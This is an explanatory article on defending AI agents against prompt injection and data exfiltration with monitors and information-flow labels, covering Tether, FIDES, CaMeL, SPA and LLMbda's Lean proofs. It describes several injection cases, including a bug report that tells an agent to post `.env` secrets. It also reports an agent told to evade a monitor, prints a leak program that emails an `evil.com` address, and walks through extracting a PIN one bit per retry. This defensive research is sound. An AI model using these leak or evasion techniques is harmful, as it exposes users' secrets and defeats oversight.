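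Zhou and colleagues also combined ELBA with an existing Haskell library for information-flow control and tested it on the Slack tasks in AgentDojo. Depending on the model, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 tasks with its policies on and 14 to 18 with them off. In a harsher test, they made every model that read an injected instruction obey it. All 735 attack attempts per model failed with the policies on, while between 114 and 310 succeeded with them off.

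### Running the command first

ELBA's approach would exclude most of a programming agent's work, because the agent needs compilers, test suites and package installers that other people wrote in other languages. *Tether*, by researchers at Google DeepMind, Google and two universities, lets the agent run any command but keeps the effects provisional. The monitor runs each command in a disposable layer over the file system, so the command can read the real files but writes only to the layer. A local proxy holds each outgoing network request.

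While a command runs, Tether records its system calls (the requests a program makes to the operating system) and translates them into 11 kinds of abstract action. If the policy permits all the actions, Tether copies the command's changes to the real file system; otherwise it discards them. It can't take back a network request, so it checks all the actions so far before forwarding one.

In the paper's main example, a company wants to keep its inventory, `servers.csv`, from reaching an outside site, while the agent may still upload harmless status reports there. The user labels the inventory Sensitive and all other files Public. Write σ(f) for the label of file f, and a ⊑ b if label a is no more restrictive than b, so Public ⊑ Sensitive. The policy allows an upload of f only if

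σ(f) ⊑ Public.

When a command copies file f to file g, Tether updates the label of g to

σ(g) = σ(f) ⊔ ℓ,

where ℓ is the label of the folder that contains g, here Public, and ⊔ picks the more restrictive of two labels. The agent now proposes three commands:

| Command | Inferred action | Label of `report.txt` afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Upload `report.txt` | upload | Public | Allow |
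| Copy `servers.csv` over `report.txt` | copy | Sensitive ⊔ Public = Sensitive | Allow |
| Upload `report.txt` | upload | Sensitive | **Block** |

The first and third commands are identical, so no filter that reads only the command's text could allow one and block the other. If the agent copies the inventory through several temporary files, each copy receives the Sensitive label and Tether still blocks the upload. A report copied from a public template remains Public, and the agent can send it.

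A monitor without labels would have to search its history for such chains of copies. The paper discusses Dogwood, Amazon's extension of Cedar that adds conditions on past events. Dogwood's rules cannot be recursive, so the developer needs a separate pattern for each possible chain. With three kinds of copying action, covering chains of up to four copies requires 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 = 120 patterns, and a chain of five matches none of them.

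Tether also keeps a label T for the model's context. Copying a file doesn't change T, because the contents never enter the context. But if a command prints the inventory, the text enters the context and T becomes Sensitive. The fuller version of the policy allows an upload to an outside site only if T ⊔ σ(f) is Public, so the agent can't upload even a harmless report there for the rest of the session. Once sensitive data is in the context, Tether is about as coarse as FORGE.

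### Why a read followed by a write counts as a flow

System calls show which files a program reads and writes but not what it computes in between. Suppose a script reads the inventory, counts the rows and writes "check finished" to a log. Tether can't distinguish this script from one that writes a disguised copy of the inventory to the log. It therefore treats everything a process writes as possibly containing data from every file the process has read, and labels the log Sensitive. Processes that receive the script's output inherit its list of files.

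The list is a sound over-approximation, meaning it may include extra files but omits none whose data is in the output. A process can only write out a file's data if it has read the file or received the data from another process, so the list is sound as long as Tether observes all these steps. Tether blocks access to channels that bypass the system calls it traces, such as memory shared between processes.

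The drawback is unnecessary blocking. For example, a search through all the files on a machine also opens the secret ones, and Tether then treats the agent as having read them, even if the agent used nothing from them.

Following data this way cannot prevent some leaks. A script might read a secret and, depending on the secret's contents, either write a file or do nothing. An observer who sees no file still learns something about the secret. Schneider's argument that a monitor can't compare runs also applies here, so Tether's developers don't claim noninterference.

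### What the Lean proofs cover

Tether's policies are Lean definitions, and the monitor executes the same definitions that the proofs are about. Some proofs concern the policy language in general. For example, they show that adding a permissive rule can never override another rule's denial, and that a blocked action changes no labels.

Others concern the policy that the developers used in their tests, which has 24 rules and four levels of confidentiality: Public, Internal, Sensitive and Secret. They proved seven invariants for it, which hold for any sequence of allowed actions, however long. One states that if the agent starts without Secret data in its context, none ever enters it:

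if T ⊑ Sensitive at the start, then T ⊑ Sensitive after every allowed action.

The proof is by induction. T changes only when the agent reads a file or receives data from the network. Each action replaces T with T ⊔ σ(r), where r is the file or network source. The policy allows these actions only if σ(r) ⊑ Sensitive. If T and σ(r) are both at most Sensitive, so is the more restrictive of the two, and the invariant still holds after the action.

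A language model wrote the proofs, but Lean checks every step, so if the model makes an error, Lean rejects the proof rather than accepting a false theorem.

The proofs start from abstract actions and do not cover whether Tether infers the right ones. If Tether misses a copy, the new file keeps a Public label and the monitor allows its upload, which contradicts none of the theorems. The code that infers the actions therefore belongs to the trusted base, as do the operating system's kernel, the tracing tool, the file-system layer, the network proxy, and Lean's proof checker, compiler and runtime.

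The developers tested the inference code by generating chains of file operations whose correct labels they knew, running them through randomly chosen system mechanisms and checking the monitor's decisions against those labels. They also told an agent to try to get past the monitor. Its success rate was 40% against an early version and 0% against the third, after the developers had fixed gaps that the proofs alone would not have revealed, such as untracked hard links, which give one file a second name.

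### Results, and what was in scope

The developers replayed recorded runs of programming agents from two benchmarks, some harmless and some with an attack. Tether blocked every attack that was in scope:

| Benchmark | Attacks blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| LinuxArena | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |

For comparison, Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews each command, caught 91.6% of the same attacks and blocked 9.7% of the harmless runs. When it also received Tether's policy as text, it caught 89.2% and blocked 3.5%, which is lower than Tether's overall false-positive rate of 4.7%.

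Of Tether's 74 false positives, 50 were edits to protected system files that the task hadn't asked for, often during software installation, and 7 were requests to undeclared sites. The developers consider the blocks in both groups correct. The remaining 17 came from commands, such as searches of the whole disk, that opened secret files.

The false-positive rates may be too low, because the developers kept running the policy on the benchmarks and revising it until it no longer blocked too many harmless runs. Even at 4.7%, if one task in 1,000 contained an attack, Tether would block about 47 harmless tasks for each attack it stopped.

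The developers had already left out runs that they couldn't replay from start to finish or whose outside services they couldn't imitate. Of the remaining runs, one was in scope if all its actions took place in the foreground, Tether could capture them, and their effects were of a kind that Tether models. This definition excludes any run with background processes or database queries. Tether can still detect both, and a stricter policy could block them or ask the user, but it would also stop legitimate database work.

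It also excludes attacks that break no rule about files, privileges or network connections, such as adding harmful code to a file the agent may edit. According to the paper, 28.2% of the runs in MonitoringBenchHonest can be judged only by their content, and the stricter policy would intercept a further 36.3%. For LinuxArena, the figures are 22.1% and 71.5%. If these are shares of all replayable runs, only about 36% of MonitoringBenchHonest and 6% of LinuxArena were in scope.

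For attacks that depend on content, the developers suggest adding a language model as a classifier. They acknowledge that the guarantee would then hold only if the classifier is correct.

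## Can labels based on origin replace detectors?

Tether blocked the upload of the copied inventory without examining its contents, because the copy had inherited the original's label. Information-flow control applies this idea to everything an agent reads. The monitor checks where an email's contents came from instead of whether they include personal data, so spelling out a phone number in words doesn't help an attacker.

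### Four labels and one email

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each piece of data a label with two parts. One part records whether the data is trusted or untrusted, and the other whether it is public or secret. As in Tether, a ⊑ b means that b is at least as restrictive as a, but now this must hold for both parts. The four possible labels then have this order:

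- (trusted, public) is the least restrictive.
- (trusted, secret) and (untrusted, public) are both above it. Neither is above the other, because each is stricter in a different part.
- (untrusted, secret) is the most restrictive.

"Untrusted" ranks above "trusted" because an agent may do less with untrusted data. The join a ⊔ b is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both a and b. For example,

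(trusted, secret) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, secret),

so a report that combines a salary file with a web page is untrusted and secret. An ordered set of labels like this one is a lattice, which means that any two labels have a join and also a counterpart below them, the most restrictive label that is no stricter than either.

The meeting notes contain company business and outsiders can edit the file, so their label is (untrusted, secret). The user's request is (trusted, public). Each sink has a limit, the most restrictive label it accepts. An email to a colleague accepts any label, and an email to an outsider accepts labels up to (untrusted, public). Deleting a calendar entry accepts labels up to (trusted, secret), so untrusted data may not influence it.

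| Step | Label of the context | Limit of the sink | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's request arrives | (trusted, public) | | |
| The agent reads the notes | (trusted, public) ⊔ (untrusted, secret) = (untrusted, secret) | | |
| It emails a summary to Alice, a colleague | (untrusted, secret) | (untrusted, secret) | Allow |
| It emails Alice's number, in words, to a stranger | (untrusted, secret) | (untrusted, public) | **Block** |
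| It deletes a calendar entry | (untrusted, secret) | (trusted, secret) | **Block** |

The monitor compared labels and looked up two addresses without calling a detector. The attacker could still distort the summary that Alice receives, because emails to colleagues may contain untrusted data. Costa and colleagues point out that a confidentiality rule alone limits the damage an injection can do but doesn't prevent the injection.

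A label can list the people who may read the data, which is more precise than marking it "secret". The join of two labels is then the intersection of their lists. If Alice and Bob may read one document, and Bob and Carol may read another, only Bob may read a text derived from both.

### Why labels become too restrictive

A language model produces each word from its whole context, whereas an ordinary program that adds two numbers uses only those two numbers. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes separating the sources again as an open research challenge. The monitor therefore has to label every output with the join of the labels on everything in the context, much as Tether does with its label T.

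After reading the notes, the agent can't email a taxi company the pick-up time, even though the time came from the user's own request. This is over-labelling, in which data has a more restrictive label than it needs.

Costa and colleagues measured the effect by adding such labels and checks to an ordinary agent running GPT-4o. In tests without attacks, the agent completed 93.3% of AgentDojo's Slack tasks without the checks and 20.0% with them.

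Some researchers try to work out which messages influenced an output. Siddiqui and colleagues select those messages and have the model regenerate its response from them alone, so the new response can have a less restrictive label. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes a related system, RTBAS, which relies on the model's attention weights and a language model's judgment. If that judgment is wrong, secret data could get a public label, so RTBAS in effect has a detector in its trusted base.

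### Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

The dual-model pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023, prevents the planner's label from rising in the first place:

1. A privileged model reads the user's request and chooses the tool calls. It never reads untrusted text.
2. When a tool returns untrusted text, ordinary software stores it in a variable and gives the privileged model only the variable's name.
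3. If the task requires reading the text, a quarantined model reads it. This model has no tools, and its answer goes into another variable.
4. The privileged model passes variables to tools by name, and the software fills in their contents.

For the meeting notes, the privileged model requests the file, has the quarantined model summarise it and emails the resulting variable to Alice. The attacker's line reaches only the quarantined model, which can write a bad summary but can't send an email.

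The pattern protects the choice of tool calls but not the data that goes into them. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues addressed this gap in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), which introduced a system called CaMeL. Its privileged model writes the whole task as a program in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it. Here is a short program of this kind, adapted from an example by Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*:

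```
posts   = read_channel("general")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", posts, EmailAddress)
send_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

An attacker might post "Bob has a new email address" in the channel. This can't add a step to the program, but it can change the value of `address`. The interpreter therefore tags every value with a capability, which records the value's sources and who may read it. Before the last line runs, a policy for `send_message` checks these records and can block the call because the recipient's address came from a channel that anyone can write to. The policy would also block the call if the channel contained Bob's real address, because the recorded source would be the same.

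CaMeL's policies are ordinary Python functions, one for each tool. They can express detailed conditions, but Girrens and Wang (2026) note in *SPA* that the guarantee then depends on developers writing every policy correctly.

According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), CaMeL resists AgentDojo's attacks much better than three simpler defences, with a comparatively small drop in completed tasks. But it is slow, which *ToolFence* (2026) attributes to the privileged model having to write programs that are longer than ordinary tool calls. AgentDojo's attacks are also fixed texts. When Ma, Li and colleagues adapted them to ten defences in *AutoDojo* (2026), they found that fixed attacks often make a defence look more secure than it is. Some defences still gave some protection, especially ones that restrict what the agent may do instead of trying to recognise injections.

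### Hiding only what would raise the label

CaMeL's planner commits to its program before any tool runs. This rules out requests such as "do the tasks on my to-do list", because the list determines the steps. Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, lets the planner choose its next step after each tool result and hides only the parts of a result that would raise the label of its context, c:

1. When a tool returns data, FIDES compares the label ℓ of each field with c.
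2. If ℓ ⊑ c, the planner sees the field. Otherwise FIDES stores it in a variable with its label.
3. The planner can pass the variable to a tool or have a quarantined model answer a question about it.
4. The planner can also open the variable. The contents then enter its context, and c becomes c ⊔ ℓ.
5. Before each tool call, FIDES checks the labels of the call and its arguments against the tool's policy.

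A policy can treat the arguments differently. For instance, it can require a trusted recipient but accept untrusted text in the message. The planner can then send a summary of a web page to Alice, but the page can't determine who receives it.

Sometimes the planner needs one fact from a hidden text, such as whether an email asks for a meeting. FIDES can force the quarantined model to answer only yes or no, and a policy may let the planner act on the answer. An attacker can still make the answer wrong but can't put an instruction into it.

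Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, without this yes-or-no feature. With GPT-4o and the policy checks off, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, none succeeded against either. These counts follow a manual review, in which the researchers excluded three successes that AgentDojo's scoring had recorded against FIDES with the checks on. They did so for reasons such as FIDES having blocked the call or the policy having allowed it.

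The zero also depends on how they chose the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so none of those attacks could come through a field they had wrongly trusted. A company can't choose labels this way because it doesn't know which fields future attacks will use.

These are the shares of tasks completed without an attack:

| GPT-4o agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Mean |
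|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, checks off | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 84.3% |
| Ordinary, checks on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 41.9% |
| FIDES, checks off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% | 60.6% |
| FIDES, checks on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 50.0% |

Switching the checks on lowers the ordinary agent's task completion rate by about 42 percentage points on average and FIDES's by about 11. But FIDES completes fewer tasks than the ordinary agent even with the checks off, partly because GPT-4o confused variable names and made unnecessary calls. FIDES did better with a stronger model, completing 68% of the travel tasks with o1 and the checks on, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

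A better model can't recover every task, because in about 44% of the banking tasks the right steps depend on what the agent reads. For example, a user may ask the agent to read a file and follow the payment instructions in it. Opening the file makes the context untrusted, so the policy blocks the payment.

Hiding data can also lead a model to make worse decisions without breaking any rule. In one banking task, the user asked the model to change the password if any recent transaction looked suspicious. FIDES hid the subject of an untrusted transaction but showed the amounts and dates. The model judged a large payment suspicious and changed the password without reading what the payment was for. AgentDojo counted this as a success.

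### Checking the whole plan before it runs

FIDES and CaMeL check each call when the agent reaches it, so a task can fail halfway, for example after sending an email. Girrens and Wang's system, SPA, checks the whole plan before running any of it. Its planner runs once per request and writes the complete plan from six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, display something, branch and loop.

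A checker then goes through the plan in order. It keeps a label for every variable, and a further label, pc, for the decisions that led to the current step. A step that uses the variables x₁, …, xₙ gets the label

pc ⊔ ℓ(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(xₙ).

If this label exceeds the limit of the tool that the step calls, SPA rejects the whole plan and runs none of it.

The label pc also catches leaks through decisions, which Tether can't prevent and FIDES's guarantee doesn't cover. Suppose a plan sends a client the message "please call me" only if the secret meeting notes mention a delay. Inside the branch, pc includes the notes' label, so SPA rejects the plan.

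SPA also keeps labels between requests. In Girrens and Wang's example, on Monday an agent reads an invoice that contains an attacker's account number. On Tuesday the user asks it to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". The planner receives only a description of the stored invoice, and the account number is still labeled untrusted. If the payment tool requires trusted inputs, SPA rejects the plan.

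Girrens and Wang tested SPA with the model gpt-5.4-nano on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and in 949 runs with an attack. They also built AgentDojo-MQ, which splits each task into several requests:

| Benchmark | Tasks completed, checks off | Tasks completed, checks on | Attacks succeeding, checks off | Attacks succeeding, checks on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 53.0% | 29.0% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| AgentDojo-MQ | 62.5% | 35.3% | 0.3% | 0.2% |

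On AgentDojo, the label checks lowered task completion by 24 percentage points and prevented four successful attacks. Planning before reading had already stopped almost all the attacks, since most of them try to insert new instructions. These results provide little evidence about attacks that only change an account number, where the checks matter most. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that the benchmark is also a weak test of delayed attacks.

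With the checks on, about 53% of AgentDojo runs ended with a rejected plan, typically because the plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that requires trusted inputs. SPA does not let the planner try again because Girrens and Wang worry that the planner could revise an unsafe plan until the checker accepts it.

CaMeLoT, by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks CaMeL's programs before they run. If a program could break a rule, CaMeLoT shows the planner how and prompts it to repair the program. Retries give an attacker more chances to get past a detector, but if the checker is sound, any program that passes complies with the policy, however many attempts it took.

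### Asking for approval less often

The comparison with an unprotected agent puts label checks at a slight disadvantage. Kolluri and colleagues point out that many real agents ask a person to approve consequential actions, but benchmarks don't count those approvals against the unprotected agent. A monitor with labels needs to ask for approval only when it can't show that an action complies.

Their own agent, Prudentia, builds on FIDES and tries to avoid such actions when it plans. It receives each tool's policy and the label of its context. Before it opens a variable, it must write down why it needs to and which calls will follow. It can also ask the user to vouch for a text once, so an email that lists ten tasks needs one approval instead of ten.

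The results for GPT-5 on AgentDojo are:

| GPT-5 agent | Completed without approvals | Completed with unlimited approvals | Approvals needed in completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, asks before every consequential action | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Ordinary with label checks | 43.4% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

With GPT-4o, however, Prudentia needed 23.8 approvals and FIDES only 7.8. Kolluri and colleagues report that reasoning models handle the extra rules better. With GPT-4o, Prudentia also cost four to ten times as much per task, on average, as the ordinary agent with label checks, though the researchers had not tried to reduce the cost.

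No people took part in these tests. The researchers counted the actions that would have required approval and assumed a person would approve the legitimate ones and stop the attacks. In practice, people who receive many requests start to approve them without thinking, which is a reason to ask less often.

In a second test, with browser agents on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, Prudentia blocked every attack and needed no approvals. The users' tasks were to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never had to open untrusted text.

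### Labels in a commercial framework

Microsoft has added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature. Each piece of data has one label for trust (trusted or untrusted) and one for confidentiality (public, private or "user identity", the most sensitive level). When data is combined, the framework keeps the most restrictive value of each label.

The documentation's example is an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. An attacker's report tells it to read `.env`, a file of secret settings, and post the contents as a comment. The report is labeled untrusted and public. Reading the file makes the context private, and the comment tool accepts only public data, so the framework blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it.

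The same settings interfere with the agent's ordinary work. The agent reads files so that it can quote relevant code in its comments, but the file-reading tool labels every file private. Once the agent has read any file, it can't comment without approval. Its tool for correcting typos in files can't run once the agent has read a bug report. Microsoft lists over-labelling among the feature's current limitations and offers a trial mode that records what the rules would have blocked.

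If a developer forgets to label a tool's output, the framework treats it as untrusted and public. Microsoft describes this default as secure. Treating the output as untrusted is cautious, but salary data from an unlabelled tool would also count as public.

### When one source holds different kinds of data

Labels can replace a detector if the rule is itself about origin, such as "nothing from the personnel database leaves the company". They work less well if the rule is about content and one source holds several kinds of content. For example, an inbox might contain lunch invitations, invoices and test results from a clinic. Labelling the whole inbox secret stops the agent from telling a client that a meeting has moved, while labelling it public means the test results can leak.

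Some finer labels can be assigned without judging the content. Costa and colleagues suggest that an email's permitted readers could be its sender and recipients, which a program can get from the header. The agent could then quote an email back to the client who sent it. But suppose Alice writes to the user that the meeting has moved and that she is in hospital. Both facts have the same origin and the same permitted readers, although the user would pass on only the news about the meeting. A person or a detector has to read the email to label the two facts separately.

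Trust labels have the same limitation. A genuine invoice and a forged one that arrive through the same channel get the same label, so a policy that blocks payment to the forged account number also blocks payment to the genuine one. Someone has to check the account number against another source to tell which invoice is genuine.

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes FlowSeal, a system that combines labels with a detector. FlowSeal labels sensitive records with their owner, based on where the records came from. A program outside the agent's model intercepts everything the agent tries to write or share. When a protected record may be involved, a separate language model compares the record with the proposed text and judges whether the text reveals it. This model doesn't receive the agent's conversation, so an attacker can't manipulate it directly.

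In one of the attacks tested, a man's ex-wife sets up a shared page and asks a colleague's agent to fill in its section, which leads the agent to write about the man's health. FlowSeal reduced the leak rate for this type of attack from 52.2% to 0.5%. Across all tests, between 0% and 3.3% of the sensitive items still leaked. The labels determine when the text is compared with the record, but a language model still decides whether the text reveals the record, and it can be wrong.

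## What has been proved about information-flow control for agents?

A label protects data only if the system attaches it to everything the data influences. CaMeL, FIDES and SPA each have rules for copying labels, and if the rules miss one kind of influence, secret data can carry a public label when it reaches a sink. To prove that this never happens, researchers need a definition of influence that doesn't depend on the rules, and they usually choose noninterference.

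### Comparing two runs

When the manager asks the agent whether an employee is free on Thursday, noninterference requires the same reply whatever the employee's secret calendar contains. The definition therefore compares two runs of the agent that differ only in the calendar.

For the formal version, choose a label n and an observer who can see only data with labels up to n. Write s₀ ~ₙ s₁ if the states s₀ and s₁ differ only in data that this observer can't see. Let e(s) be the state in which program e finishes if it starts from s. A deterministic program, which always gives the same result from the same start, satisfies noninterference if, for every n,

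s₀ ~ₙ s₁ implies e(s₀) ~ₙ e(s₁).

The same formula covers trust. If the observer sees only trusted data, the two starting states may differ in anything an attacker wrote. The trusted results must still be the same, so the attacker can't influence them.

Schneider showed that a monitor watching one run of a program can't check a property that compares two runs. But a programming language can have rules so strict that every program that runs to the end has the property, though these rules also stop some harmless programs.

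Most proofs establish a weaker property, termination-insensitive noninterference, which requires equal visible results only if both runs finish. This property allows the secret to affect whether a program finishes. Label checks can cause this by stopping a run. For example, an agent might try to email the manager only if the calendar shows a medical appointment. If a label check stops the agent there, the manager can infer the appointment from the missing reply. An observer who sees only the final result learns at most one bit this way, the answer to one yes-or-no question.

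### Why a language model needs probabilities

A language model's output is usually partly random, so two runs can give different replies even if the calendar is the same. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, therefore compare the probabilities of the results. Let μ(q) be the probability that the agent finishes with visible result q for one value of the secret, and ν(q) the same probability for another value. μ and ν are subdistributions, which means that the probabilities in each can add up to less than 1. The missing probability is the chance that a run never finishes, for example because a label check stops it.

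If every run finished, the obvious requirement would be μ = ν. To allow for unfinished runs, Garby and colleagues first tried comparing the probabilities among finished runs only, but this turned out to be the wrong definition. Here is an invented example of the problem. An agent begins its reply with "Hi" or "Hello", each with probability 0.5. If it has chosen "Hello" and the calendar shows an appointment, a label check stops it:

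| Visible result | μ: no appointment | ν: appointment |
|---|---|---|
| "Hi" | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| "Hello" | 0.5 | 0 |
| Run does not finish | 0 | 0.5 |

Among runs that finish, 50% produce "Hi" when there is no appointment and 100% do when there is one. The comparison would therefore reject this program, even though the secret affects only whether it finishes.

The definition they settled on requires μ and ν to be compatible. This means that there is a third subdistribution ω, with a total of at most 1, such that for every result q

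μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q).

Both columns could then become equal if more of the unfinished runs had finished. In the example, ω can give 0.5 to each greeting. If instead every run finished, and changing the secret lowered the chance of "Hi" from 60% to 40% and raised the chance of "Hello" from 40% to 60%, ω would have to give each greeting at least 0.6. The total would be at least 1.2, above the limit of 1, so μ and ν would not be compatible.

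Compatibility also limits how much an observer can learn. Let div(μ) be the probability that a run does not finish. The difference between the visible results satisfies

½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2.

In the example, the left side is ½ × (0 + 0.5) = 0.25, and the right side is (0 + 0.5) / 2, which is also 0.25. If both programs always finish, the right side is zero, so μ and ν must be equal.

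The sum omits the case where no reply arrives, which an observer may also notice. Counting "no reply" as a result raises the difference in the example to 0.5. In general, the difference can be as large as the greater of the two probabilities of not finishing. So the more often label checks stop an agent, the less this bound guarantees, even if every stop is correct.

### Labels in the LLMbda calculus

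Garby and colleagues proved termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference for LLMbda, a small programming language in which developers can write whole agents. LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions, with operations on a conversation with a language model. A program can send a message, receive the reply, clear the conversation, or "fork" it, working on a temporary copy before returning to the original. The reply may contain code, which the program then runs.

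Every value has a label, and a value computed from several others gets the join of their labels. The conversation's label is the join of the labels of everything the program has sent since it last cleared the conversation. The model's reply gets at least this label, regardless of its wording.

Like SPA, LLMbda has a program-counter label, pc, which gives everything a branch computes at least the label of the decision that led to it. Code in the model's reply runs with pc equal to the conversation's label. So if a model reads an attacker's email and then writes a program, that program can produce only untrusted values.

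The dual-model pattern doesn't need special support in this language. A program can query a quarantined model by forking the conversation, clearing the copy and sending the query there. The answer is still untrusted, but the email never enters the main conversation, whose label doesn't change.

One further rule controls changes to the conversation. A program may send a message only if

pc ⊑ the conversation's current label.

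An example in the paper shows why. A program takes these steps:

1. It tells the model, "Remember this value: x = false."
2. If a secret is true, it tells the model, "Set x = true."
3. It asks the model for x.

Raising the conversation's label to secret in step 2 protects the secret only if it is true. If the secret is false, step 2 doesn't run, the conversation stays public, and anyone who may see public data can learn the secret by reading the answer "false". LLMbda therefore stops the program in step 2 if the secret is true, because the branch is secret and the conversation is public. Researchers call this rule "no high upgrade".

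Now let a state s include the program, its data and the conversation, and let ⟦s⟧ₙ be the subdistribution of results that an observer with label n can see. The main theorem states that, for every n,

if s₀ ~ₙ s₁, then ⟦s₀⟧ₙ and ⟦s₁⟧ₙ are compatible.

The theorem holds for every LLMbda program that doesn't deliberately lower a label, including programs that run code the model has just written. It assumes that the probability of each model reply depends only on the conversation so far, but it assumes nothing about how well the model behaves.

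### How the proof works

The proof requires a suitable ω for any two states that look the same to the observer. Garby and colleagues construct it by defining a second way to run programs, which skips the computation and substitutes an empty value as soon as a label goes beyond what the observer can see. In the example with the two greetings, it would skip the step that depends on the calendar and always finish, giving "Hi" and "Hello" a probability of 0.5 each.

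Let ω₀ and ω₁ be the results of running the two states with skipping. The proof establishes three facts:

- Skipping never makes a visible result less likely, because a computation that has been skipped can't stop the program or run forever. So μ ≤ ω₀ and ν ≤ ω₁.
- Skipping gives the same probabilities for both states, because it never uses the data in which they differ. So ω₀ = ω₁.
- The probabilities in ω₀ add up to at most 1.

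Together these give μ ≤ ω₀ = ω₁ ≥ ν, so ω₀ is the ω that the definition requires.

Geoffrey Smith and Rafael Alpízar used a similar argument in 2011 for simple programs with random choices. They deleted the secret-dependent parts of the program's text in advance. That isn't possible for an agent that writes code as it works, because some of the text doesn't exist yet. Skipping those parts at run time works, but it requires 76 rules, and a person checking every case by hand could easily miss one.

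Lean checks the proofs of all the theorems. The interpreter that runs LLMbda agents is also a Lean function. It takes the model's replies from a table fixed in advance, so it is deterministic for any given table. A further theorem shows that if the table's entries are drawn at random with the model's probabilities, the interpreter's results have exactly the distribution described in the noninterference theorem.

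In one of the paper's examples, a program calls the model twice to flip a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, then counts the heads. Both methods of calculation give probabilities of 0.49 for no heads, 0.42 for one and 0.09 for two.

The trusted base still includes Lean's proof checker and compiler, and the code that contacts the model over the network. The theorem about the answer book also assumes that the model draws each reply independently, with fixed probabilities for each conversation.

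### The branch CaMeL did not take

Garby and colleagues also examined CaMeL's interpreter and found a leak that J. S. Fenton had described for ordinary programs in 1974. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email inside a secret branch, such as "if the balance is above the threshold, send an email". This program gets the same information out through two variables:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
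if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret. When CaMeL changes a variable inside a secret branch, it labels the variable secret, but it does so only if the branch runs:

| Step | Balance above threshold | Balance not above threshold |
|---|---|---|
| First two lines | `rich` and `tmp` are true and public | `rich` and `tmp` are true and public |
| `if balance > threshold` | Runs: `tmp` becomes false and **secret** | Skipped: `tmp` stays true and public |
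| `if tmp` | Skipped: `rich` stays true and **public** | Runs: `rich` becomes false and public |
| `if rich` | **Sends the email** | Sends nothing |

In the left column, `rich` depends on the balance but has a public label, because CaMeL skipped the line that would have changed it. The email then passes the label check, and the attacker learns that the balance is above the threshold. Under a no-high-upgrade rule, the program would stop at the third line, where a branch that depends on secret data would change a public variable.

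An attacker can't normally insert this program, because CaMeL's planner writes the code before the system reads any untrusted text. But the planner could write an equivalent program by mistake, and a noninterference proof would have to cover that program too.

Another reported fault concerns how CaMeL handles text. If a program inserts an untrusted value into a text template, CaMeL treats the result as trusted, so an attacker's account number could lose its untrusted label.

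### From one bit to a whole secret

The second main gap is the retry loop, which runs outside CaMeL's interpreter. If a program fails, ordinary Python code reports the error to the planner and asks for a new program. This code doesn't track labels, so each attempt starts without any label from the previous one. Yet whether a program fails can depend on a secret, because a label check may stop the program in a branch that runs only for certain values of the secret.

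Suppose the secret is a four-digit PIN. The first program attempts a forbidden action only if the PIN is above 4999. If the label check stops it, the next program tests whether the PIN is above 7499, and otherwise whether it is above 2499. Each program halves the remaining range, so 14 programs are enough to find the PIN (2¹⁴ = 16,384, which is more than the 10,000 possible values). Termination-insensitive noninterference allows each program to leak only one bit, but running the programs in a loop leaks the whole PIN.

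CaMeL censors error messages before the planner reads them, because its developers recognised that the messages could carry data. This reduces the leak but, as Garby and colleagues point out, gives no formal guarantee. CaMeL has no noninterference theorem, so the two gaps do not contradict a proved result. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's developers call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

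In LLMbda, the retry loop has to be part of the program, and no program can catch a failed label check and continue, so a run can fail at most one check. But the theorem covers only a single run. If a scheduler outside LLMbda restarted the agent after every failure and passed it information about the failure, the leak through retries would return.

### What the FIDES theorem covers

Costa and colleagues proved a theorem about FIDES, but its confidentiality part concerns explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. A run satisfies explicit secrecy if repeating the same operations with only the secret data changed would produce the same outputs. Unlike noninterference, this ignores how the secret influenced the choice of operations.

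An agent might send the manager "busy" if the calendar shows an appointment and "free" if it doesn't. In a run with an appointment, the operation is "send the fixed word 'busy'". Performing that same operation with a different calendar would still send "busy", so the run satisfies explicit secrecy. It violates noninterference because the agent would have sent "free" if the calendar had shown no appointment.

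A program can also leak a long secret this way. It can test each binary digit of the PIN and add a fixed "0" or "1" to a message, so the finished message contains the whole PIN even though the program never copied it. Garby and colleagues argue that explicit secrecy is weakest for systems like agents, in which data can become instructions. The two theorems also differ in scope. The FIDES theorem covers a single planning loop, whose tools can vary, and treats the model as a deterministic function.

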